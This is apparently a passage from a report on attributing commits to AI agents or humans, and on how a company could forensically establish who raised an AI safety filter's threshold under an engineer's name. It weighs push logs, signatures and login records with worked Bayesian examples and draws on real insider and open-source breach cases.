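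*Who Finishes the Job?*, a study of coding agents, classifies a commit as human if it has neither an agent's login nor a recognisable marker in its message. The researchers therefore present their figures for agents' work as a lower bound. They left OpenAI's Codex out of the comparison because so few of its commits have a marker. This method may be adequate for a cautious estimate across thousands of commits, but its "human" label would be poor evidence of who made a single disputed change.

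*Agent or Human* (Horikawa, Li and colleagues, 2026) addresses how to identify agents' commits when these markers are missing. Even with a reliable detector, an investigator would still need to know who started the agent and what that person asked for.

### How often do developers disclose AI's work?

*The AI Attribution Paradox* (Kraishan, 2025) studied 14,300 commits made in 7,393 GitHub repositories between January 2023 and December 2025. Its summary reports that 95.2% of the commits used AI but only 29.5% disclosed it explicitly. The data cannot show that most developers who use AI conceal it, although the summary gives that impression.

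Kraishan found the commits by searching for the names of AI tools and phrases such as "ai generated", so nearly all of them were bound to mention AI. The 95.2% is a product of the search, not an estimate of how many developers use these tools. A program then sorted the commits by the wording of their messages:

- 4,215 commits (29.5%) credited a tool with producing the work, for example "generated by Copilot".
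- 142 commits (1.0%) acknowledged a tool's help without calling it the author.
- 9,260 commits (64.8%) mentioned a tool without crediting it.
- 683 commits (4.8%) contained none of the AI terms.

The third group includes messages such as "Adding Copilot support", which describe work on software that connects to an AI tool. A developer could have written every line of such a change. One of the search terms also seems to have been "cursor", which is both the name of an AI code editor and an ordinary programming word. Only 4,357 commits had messages crediting AI with any part in the work, about 97% of them explicitly. The search was unlikely to find commits in which developers used AI and left no trace of it.

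Among commits associated with Anthropic's Claude, 80.5% had explicit attribution, compared with 9.0% for GitHub Copilot. Kraishan interprets attribution as a strategy developers use to balance openness against the risk of criticism. The tools' own behaviour may explain much of the difference between the two tools, because some agents add a line such as "Generated by: Claude" to their commits. A developer who leaves that line in may not have thought about disclosure at all. The growing use of these agents could also help explain why explicit attribution rose from almost nothing in early 2024 to 40% in late 2025.

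Developers may still have a reason to remove the attribution line. Commits with explicit attribution received 23% more questions and 21% more comments, although the tone of the discussion stayed neutral.

Kraishan also gives the sample's minimum as 100 stars, the bookmarks that GitHub users add to repositories they like, but reports that 92.8% of the commits came from repositories with fewer. The results therefore come mostly from small projects and are a poor guide to large ones or to the private repositories of AI companies.

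*Perspective on AI and quantum open-source software* (2026) provides newer figures for 19 scientific projects, based on disclosures of AI use in commit messages and pull request text. In the median quantum-computing project, 0.43% of pull requests from 2026 included such a disclosure, compared with 4.56% in the median project from a group of widely used scientific tools. All eight of the widely used tools ask contributors to disclose AI use, but only three of the eleven quantum projects do, so the difference may reflect the projects' rules more than how much AI their contributors use.

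One developer's habits can also skew a project's figures. In one of the 19 projects, half of all commits from 2026 disclosed AI involvement, but a single maintainer made 1,107 of those 1,145 commits. The other contributors may have used AI just as often without recording it.

Projects have different rules for disclosing AI use. *AI Policy, Disclosure, and Human in the Loop* (2026) found that projects commonly ask contributors to name the tool, describe how much it helped and add a line such as "Assisted-By:" to the commit. The picoclaw project requires contributors to say whether a change is fully AI-generated, mostly AI-generated or mostly human-written. The project behind Terraform, a program for managing servers and other infrastructure, asks agents and their users to identify themselves in pull request titles. The study does not establish whether contributors follow such rules.

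In a dispute over a safety threshold, picoclaw's categories would be more useful than a simple co-author line, because the first category means that the contributor reviewed and validated AI-written code. But contributors choose the category themselves, so a forger could pick whichever looked least suspicious.

A company has more control over agents on its own systems than an open-source project has over its contributors. It can give each agent a separate account and signing key instead of letting it use a developer's, and it can record who started each session. OpenAI's *Securing persistent agents like OpenClaw at OpenAI* lists "agent identity" among the company's measures for long-running agents. If an agent with its own identity changed a threshold, the push log could distinguish its work from Ana's, provided that neither Ana nor other agents could use its credentials.

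## How could one establish who changed a safety threshold?

Suppose an AI company's filter scores each request to its chatbot from 0 to 1. A commit on 3 March 2026 raises the blocking threshold from 0.80 to 0.95, so the filter now lets through a request with a score of 0.87, which it would have blocked the day before. The commit lists Ana Ruiz, an engineer, as both author and committer. On 12 March a tester notices that the chatbot is answering requests it used to refuse. Ana denies making the change.

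Ana may have made the change herself. A colleague may have typed her name into a commit and pushed it from their own account. Or somebody inside or outside the company may have used Ana's account or keys. The commit would carry her name in all three cases, so the company needs other evidence to establish who made the change.

### Saving the records

The company can restore the old threshold within minutes, and should use a new commit to do it, because a force-push could destroy the disputed commit. GitHub's guide to responding to security incidents recommends exporting logs and saving copies of affected files before any cleanup. It also recommends deleting malicious branches immediately, so anyone who follows it should copy the branch first.

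Investigators should first save the records that will expire soonest, whatever order they read them in. By 12 March the push is no longer in GitHub's own audit log, which keeps pushes for seven days. According to GitHub's overview of investigation tools, customers on its Free and Team plans can't see Git events in the log. The company in this example still has the entry because it had been streaming its log to separate storage.

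The Australian Signals Directorate's *Best practices for event logging and threat detection*, written with agencies from eight other countries, warns that default log retention periods are often too short because an organisation can take up to 18 months to discover an incident. It also recommends recording times in UTC. If the PHP evidence had done so, readers would not have had to convert between three time zones.

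*Incident Response Recommendations and Considerations for Cybersecurity Risk Management* (Nelson, Rekhi and colleagues, 2025) is the current guidance from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST). It recommends that organisations preserve the integrity and provenance of incident data, so that they can tell where each record came from and whether anyone has altered it. Nelson and colleagues accept that organisations may not follow formal evidence-handling procedures in every case, since most malware incidents never lead to a prosecution. But Ana could lose her job or face charges, so the formal procedure is worth the effort. Someone outside her team could export each log, compute a hash of the file, and write down the time and who has had access to it since.

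The NIST guidance doesn't include a procedure for a disputed commit. It replaced a more detailed 2012 handbook because, Nelson and colleagues explain, the details of incident response now change too often and vary too much between organisations for a single publication to cover.

### The evidence, in order

Investigators should start with copies of the repository that neither Ana nor the forge's administrators could have altered, such as one on a colleague's laptop or in an offline backup. If Ben downloaded the branch on 4 March and his copy contains the same commit hash, nobody has rewritten the commit since then. If his copy has a different commit, somebody replaced it later, and the company should investigate that change too. The log of the automated job that deployed the filter can provide another old hash if the job printed the commit it used. GitHub keeps these logs for 90 days by default.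 People can delete them earlier, but the audit log records the deletion.

The next step is to collect push logs for every route into the repository. Popov wrongly inferred a server break-in from a log that covered only one route. Developers may push over SSH or HTTPS, edit files on the website, or use a program with an access token. GitHub's list of investigation areas also includes new deploy keys, which are SSH keys attached to a repository instead of a person, and newly installed apps. According to GitHub, audit log searches on a self-hosted GitHub server do not show pushes even when the server records them, so an investigator could mistake an empty search result for proof that nobody had pushed.

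If the log shows a push from Ana's account, it is much less likely that a colleague just typed her name as the author, but someone who stole her password would leave the same entry. If the log shows Chen's account, Ana may still have written the change, because colleagues push one another's commits.

A signature from Ana's own key would rule out anyone who could not use that key, but a signature from the forge would add little to the evidence in the push log.

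Login and device records are the best chance of distinguishing Ana from someone using her account. The Australian Signals Directorate's warning signs include logins at unusual hours, from an unfamiliar device, or from two places too far apart for one person to have travelled between them, though it notes that each can have an innocent explanation. On Ana's laptop, Git's reflog may show that someone made the commit there. If it doesn't, that is weak evidence in her favour, because she could have deleted the entry or used another machine.

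The company may need Ana's help to see some of these records. GitHub includes users' logins in the company's audit log only if the company manages their accounts. If Ana uses a personal account, only she can open its security log, so the company would have to ask her for a record that might clear her. GitHub shows the IP address behind an action only if the company turned that feature on beforehand.

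Review records come last because they usually show more about who approved a change than about who made it. Ben's approval shows that his account accepted the new threshold, but not that Ana wrote it. The review discussion can be more useful. If Ana's account answered Ben's question on 3 March about false alarms, and Ben remembers talking to her about it that afternoon, she very likely knew about the change. If nobody approved the change, the audit log may show that someone removed the rule requiring approval.

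| Evidence | What it can exclude | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| Independent copies of the repository | A later rewrite of the commit | A false name from the start |
| Push logs from every route | A forger who pushed from their own account | Someone else using Ana's account, or a false log entry |
| Signature from Ana's key | Anyone unable to use the key | Theft or misuse of the key |
| Login and device records | A push from Ana's usual computer, if the records show another one | Ana using a different computer, or someone else using hers |
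| Review records | A change that nobody else saw, if colleagues remember discussing it | Who typed the new value |

### Comparing the three explanations

Bayes' rule, a formula for updating probabilities when new evidence arrives, shows how these records work together. Each explanation starts with a prior, the probability it had before the evidence. The investigator multiplies that prior by the probability of seeing each piece of evidence if the explanation were true. Ana's probability is her product divided by the sum of all three:

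P(Ana made the change) = Ana's product ÷ (Ana's product + forger's product + credential user's product)

The numbers below are illustrative and do not come from measurements.

| | Ana made the change | A colleague forged her name | Someone used her credentials |
|---|---|---|---|
| Prior | 0.90 | 0.05 | 0.05 |
| Ana's name is on the commit | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| Ana denies making it | 0.1 | 1 | 1 |
| Push log shows Ana's account | 1 | 0.02 | 1 |
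| Signature from a key that needs a physical touch | 1 | 0.001 | 0.05 |

The prior is 0.90 because most commits in an engineer's name come from that engineer. It must not take Ana's denial into account, because the denial has its own row. The table assumes that one in ten engineers who had made such a change would deny it, and that an innocent engineer always would. If a colleague forged Ana's name and pushed from their own account, the log should show that account. The 0.02 allows for an error or tampering with the log.

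Multiplying down each column gives these results:

| Evidence so far | Ana | Forged name | Used credentials | Probability that Ana did it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Name | 0.90 | 0.05 | 0.05 | 90% |
| Name and denial | 0.09 | 0.05 | 0.05 | 47% |
| Push log added | 0.09 | 0.001 | 0.05 | 64% |
| Signature added | 0.09 | 0.000001 | 0.0025 | 97% |

The name leaves the probability unchanged at 90%. The push log almost rules out a forged name but doesn't distinguish Ana from someone using her credentials, so it raises the probability that it was Ana only to 64%. The signature makes a larger difference because someone with her password usually couldn't touch her key.

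Login records could reverse the result. Suppose there were no signature, and the push came from a computer Ana had never used before. Suppose also that this had a probability of 0.5 if someone else used her credentials and 0.02 under either of the other explanations. The probability that Ana made the change would then fall from 64% to about 7%.

### How much depends on the assumptions?

The 97% depends heavily on the prior. In the next table the evidence stays the same, and the two explanations in which Ana is innocent share the rest of the prior equally.

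| Prior for Ana | After name and denial | With push log | With signature |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.90 | 47% | 64% | 97% |
| 0.50 | 9% | 16% | 80% |
| 0.10 | 1% | 2% | 31% |

A lower prior might be reasonable if, for example, the company had just learned that someone had stolen several engineers' passwords.

The likelihood ratio shows how much the evidence contributes without the prior. It is the probability of the evidence if Ana made the change, divided by its probability if she didn't. *Likelihood Ratio as Weight of Forensic Evidence* (2016) explains how to calculate it when there are several innocent explanations, by averaging their probabilities and giving more weight to those with higher priors. Here the two have equal weight:

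0.1 ÷ (0.5 × 0.00002 + 0.5 × 0.05) ≈ 4

The push log and signature multiply the odds that Ana made the change by about 40, and her denial divides them by ten. All the evidence together therefore raises the odds only about fourfold, from 9 to 1 to about 36 to 1.

The result also depends on how the company divides the remaining 10% of the prior between the two innocent explanations. With 9% for stolen credentials and 1% for a forged name, the probability that Ana made the change is 50% after the push log. With the figures swapped, it is 88%. The split did not affect the updates on the name and the denial, because each was equally likely under both innocent explanations.

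Multiplying the probabilities also assumes that the pieces of evidence are independent under each explanation. For example, if someone else used Ana's credentials, finding her account in the push log must not change the probability of finding her signature. This assumption could easily be wrong, because an intruder who controlled Ana's laptop could push from her account and might also trick her into touching her key. If that raised the probability of the signature from 0.05 to 0.5, the final result would fall from 97% to 78%.

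Ana's denial may depend on the other evidence too. Someone who has seen the push log can change their story to fit it, for example by saying that somebody must have stolen their password. The company should therefore ask Ana what she was doing on 3 March before showing her the logs. It should also be wary of assuming that only one guilty engineer in ten would lie. If half would, the denial would lower the probability that she is guilty only from 90% to 82%, and the final probability would be above 99%.

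In a later paper also titled *Likelihood Ratio as Weight of Forensic Evidence*, Lund and Iyer (2017) argue that an expert shouldn't just give a decision-maker a single ratio. People can use Bayes' rule to update their own beliefs, but it doesn't require them to adopt an expert's numbers. Lund and Iyer propose examining how much the ratio changes under different assumptions. In Ana's case, a report with the evidence and a range of results would be more honest than one that put her probability at 97%.

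### Did anyone touch the key?

The signature affects the result so much because Ana's key requires a physical touch. If the key were an ordinary file on her laptop, an intruder with access to the laptop could probably use it. Assuming a probability of 0.8 that the signature would appear if her credentials were stolen, the final result would be only 69%, barely higher than with the push log alone. The company therefore needs to know whether the key required a touch on 3 March.

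Some security keys record the touch in the signature. OpenSSH requires this record by default, but djm (2019), in *upstream*, added an option that lets a server waive it. Software that checks signatures may also ignore the record. Until a fix in 2026, the *ssh* package for the Go programming language accepted security-key signatures without checking for a touch.

Even if Ana did touch the key, she may not have approved this commit. GitLab's *Configuring and Using the Yubikey* has staff set their keys to remember a touch for 15 seconds, because touching the key for every signature would be tedious when rebasing many commits. A malicious program on the laptop could sign something else during those seconds. It could also wait until Ana expected to sign a commit, then send a different one to the key. Valsorda notes in *Touch-to-operate password-store with YubiKey 4* that an attacker can hijack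 a touch for another request. The 0.05 in the table allows for such tricks, but nobody seems to have measured how often they succeed.

### Is it worth finding out who did it?

One could object that the company should restore the filter without investigating the change. Users are safer as soon as the threshold returns to 0.80, whereas an investigation could take months and damage an innocent engineer's career. Nelson and colleagues note that a more thorough investigation may conflict with a quick return to normal operations.

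Whoever raised the threshold may be able to raise it again. At PHP, the attacker returned the same day with a different account. To prevent that, the company has to know whose access to revoke. It could revoke everyone's, but GitHub's response guide warns that such bulk measures break automated jobs and recommends reserving them for major incidents.

The push log is stronger evidence of which account was used than of who used it. Given the log, the probability that Ana made the change is only 64%, but the probability that it came through her account is over 99%, because that includes both Ana and anyone using her credentials. The company can therefore suspend the account long before it has enough evidence to accuse her. If she turns out to be innocent, it can restore her access the same day, while an accusation would be much harder to undo.

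The company still has to decide whether to give Ana new credentials. She needs them, along with a clean laptop, if someone stole the old ones, but if she made the change herself, they would give her another chance to do it. The company can suspend her account while it continues to investigate her. Nelson and colleagues recommend restricting access to the investigation's records, partly because they may name users suspected of misconduct.

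### Where the comparison with open-source breaches holds

Open-source breaches are a good guide to Ana's case where her company has the same weaknesses: unverified names, shared accounts, or an unlogged route into the repository.

The comparison is weaker if the company controls every account and device. PHP's developers worked on their own computers, which the project had few ways to examine. A company can inspect Ana's laptop, compare the push with the building's door records and interview her colleagues. It can also enforce stricter rules. In the PHP discussion started by Rethans, Larry Garfield, who was working on corporate projects, wrote that he always blocked direct pushes to the main branch and required someone other than the author to approve each change.

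But this control helps only if the culprit doesn't share it. *Former Employee Of Technology Company Sentenced To Six Years In Prison*, from the U.S. Attorney's Office, Southern District of New York, describes how Nickolas Sharp, a senior developer, stole his employer's data in December 2020. The Record's *Feds get guilty plea in Ubiquiti data extortion case* identifies the company as Ubiquiti, which makes networking equipment. Sharp used his administrative access to change how long the company kept its logs. He also renamed session files to make his colleagues look responsible. He then joined the team dealing with the breach while anonymously demanding about $1.9 million in cryptocurrency from the company.

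Sharp had hidden his location with a VPN, which conceals a user's internet address. The same office's *Former Employee Of Technology Company Pleads Guilty To Stealing Confidential Data* explains that his home internet address became visible after an internet outage. The Record adds that a log captured it while he was copying repositories from GitHub. When investigators showed him that he had bought the VPN service months earlier, he said someone else must have used his PayPal account. He later pleaded guilty, and in May 2023 a judge sentenced him to six years in prison.

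Sharp stole data and did not forge a commit or change an AI safeguard, but he could have misled an investigation that relied on his employer's session files. He had no control over his internet connection or the record of his VPN purchase. The Australian Signals Directorate recommends storing logs on a separate network, limiting who can change or delete them, and recording who accesses them. A company investigating Ana should also keep anyone who could have made the change off the team collecting the evidence, however senior they are.

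A company may lack the independent copies that help an open-source project detect tampering. Outsiders had their own copies of PHP's source code and could compare them with the server's copy, but all the copies of a private repository may be on machines managed by the same few administrators. The company can make up for this by regularly sending the latest commit hash to an outsider, such as an auditor, who doesn't need to see the code.

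### A change that is easy to miss

A changed threshold is also harder to notice than inserted code. Other developers recognised the code inserted into PHP as dangerous within hours, but in Ana's repository one valid number replaced another. The program still works and no unfamiliar code appears, so a reviewer would need to know which requests score between 0.80 and 0.95 to see the harm.

The filter's behaviour may reveal a threshold change more clearly than the commit does. Suppose the filter normally blocks about 100 requests a day, 40 of which score between the old and new thresholds. After the change, it would block about 60. If requests arrive independently, the daily count would normally vary by about 10 in either direction, so a drop of 40 should stand out. The company could also send the filter a fixed set of test requests after every deployment. Neither check would identify who made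 the change, but either could have alerted the company on 4 March, while GitHub still had the push in its log.

Some companies don't keep such settings in Git. An administrator may instead change the threshold on a web page, in a database or through a service that turns features on and off. There would then be no commit for gittuf to check. Investigators should find out which value the running filter was using, and where that value came from, before studying the commit in Ana's name.

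For cloud services, the Australian Signals Directorate lists administrative configuration changes among the events to log first. Its list of useful details includes the time, the user, the IP address and the command, but not the setting's previous value, which a Git history would supply. A company that changes thresholds outside Git needs a log that records both the old and new values.
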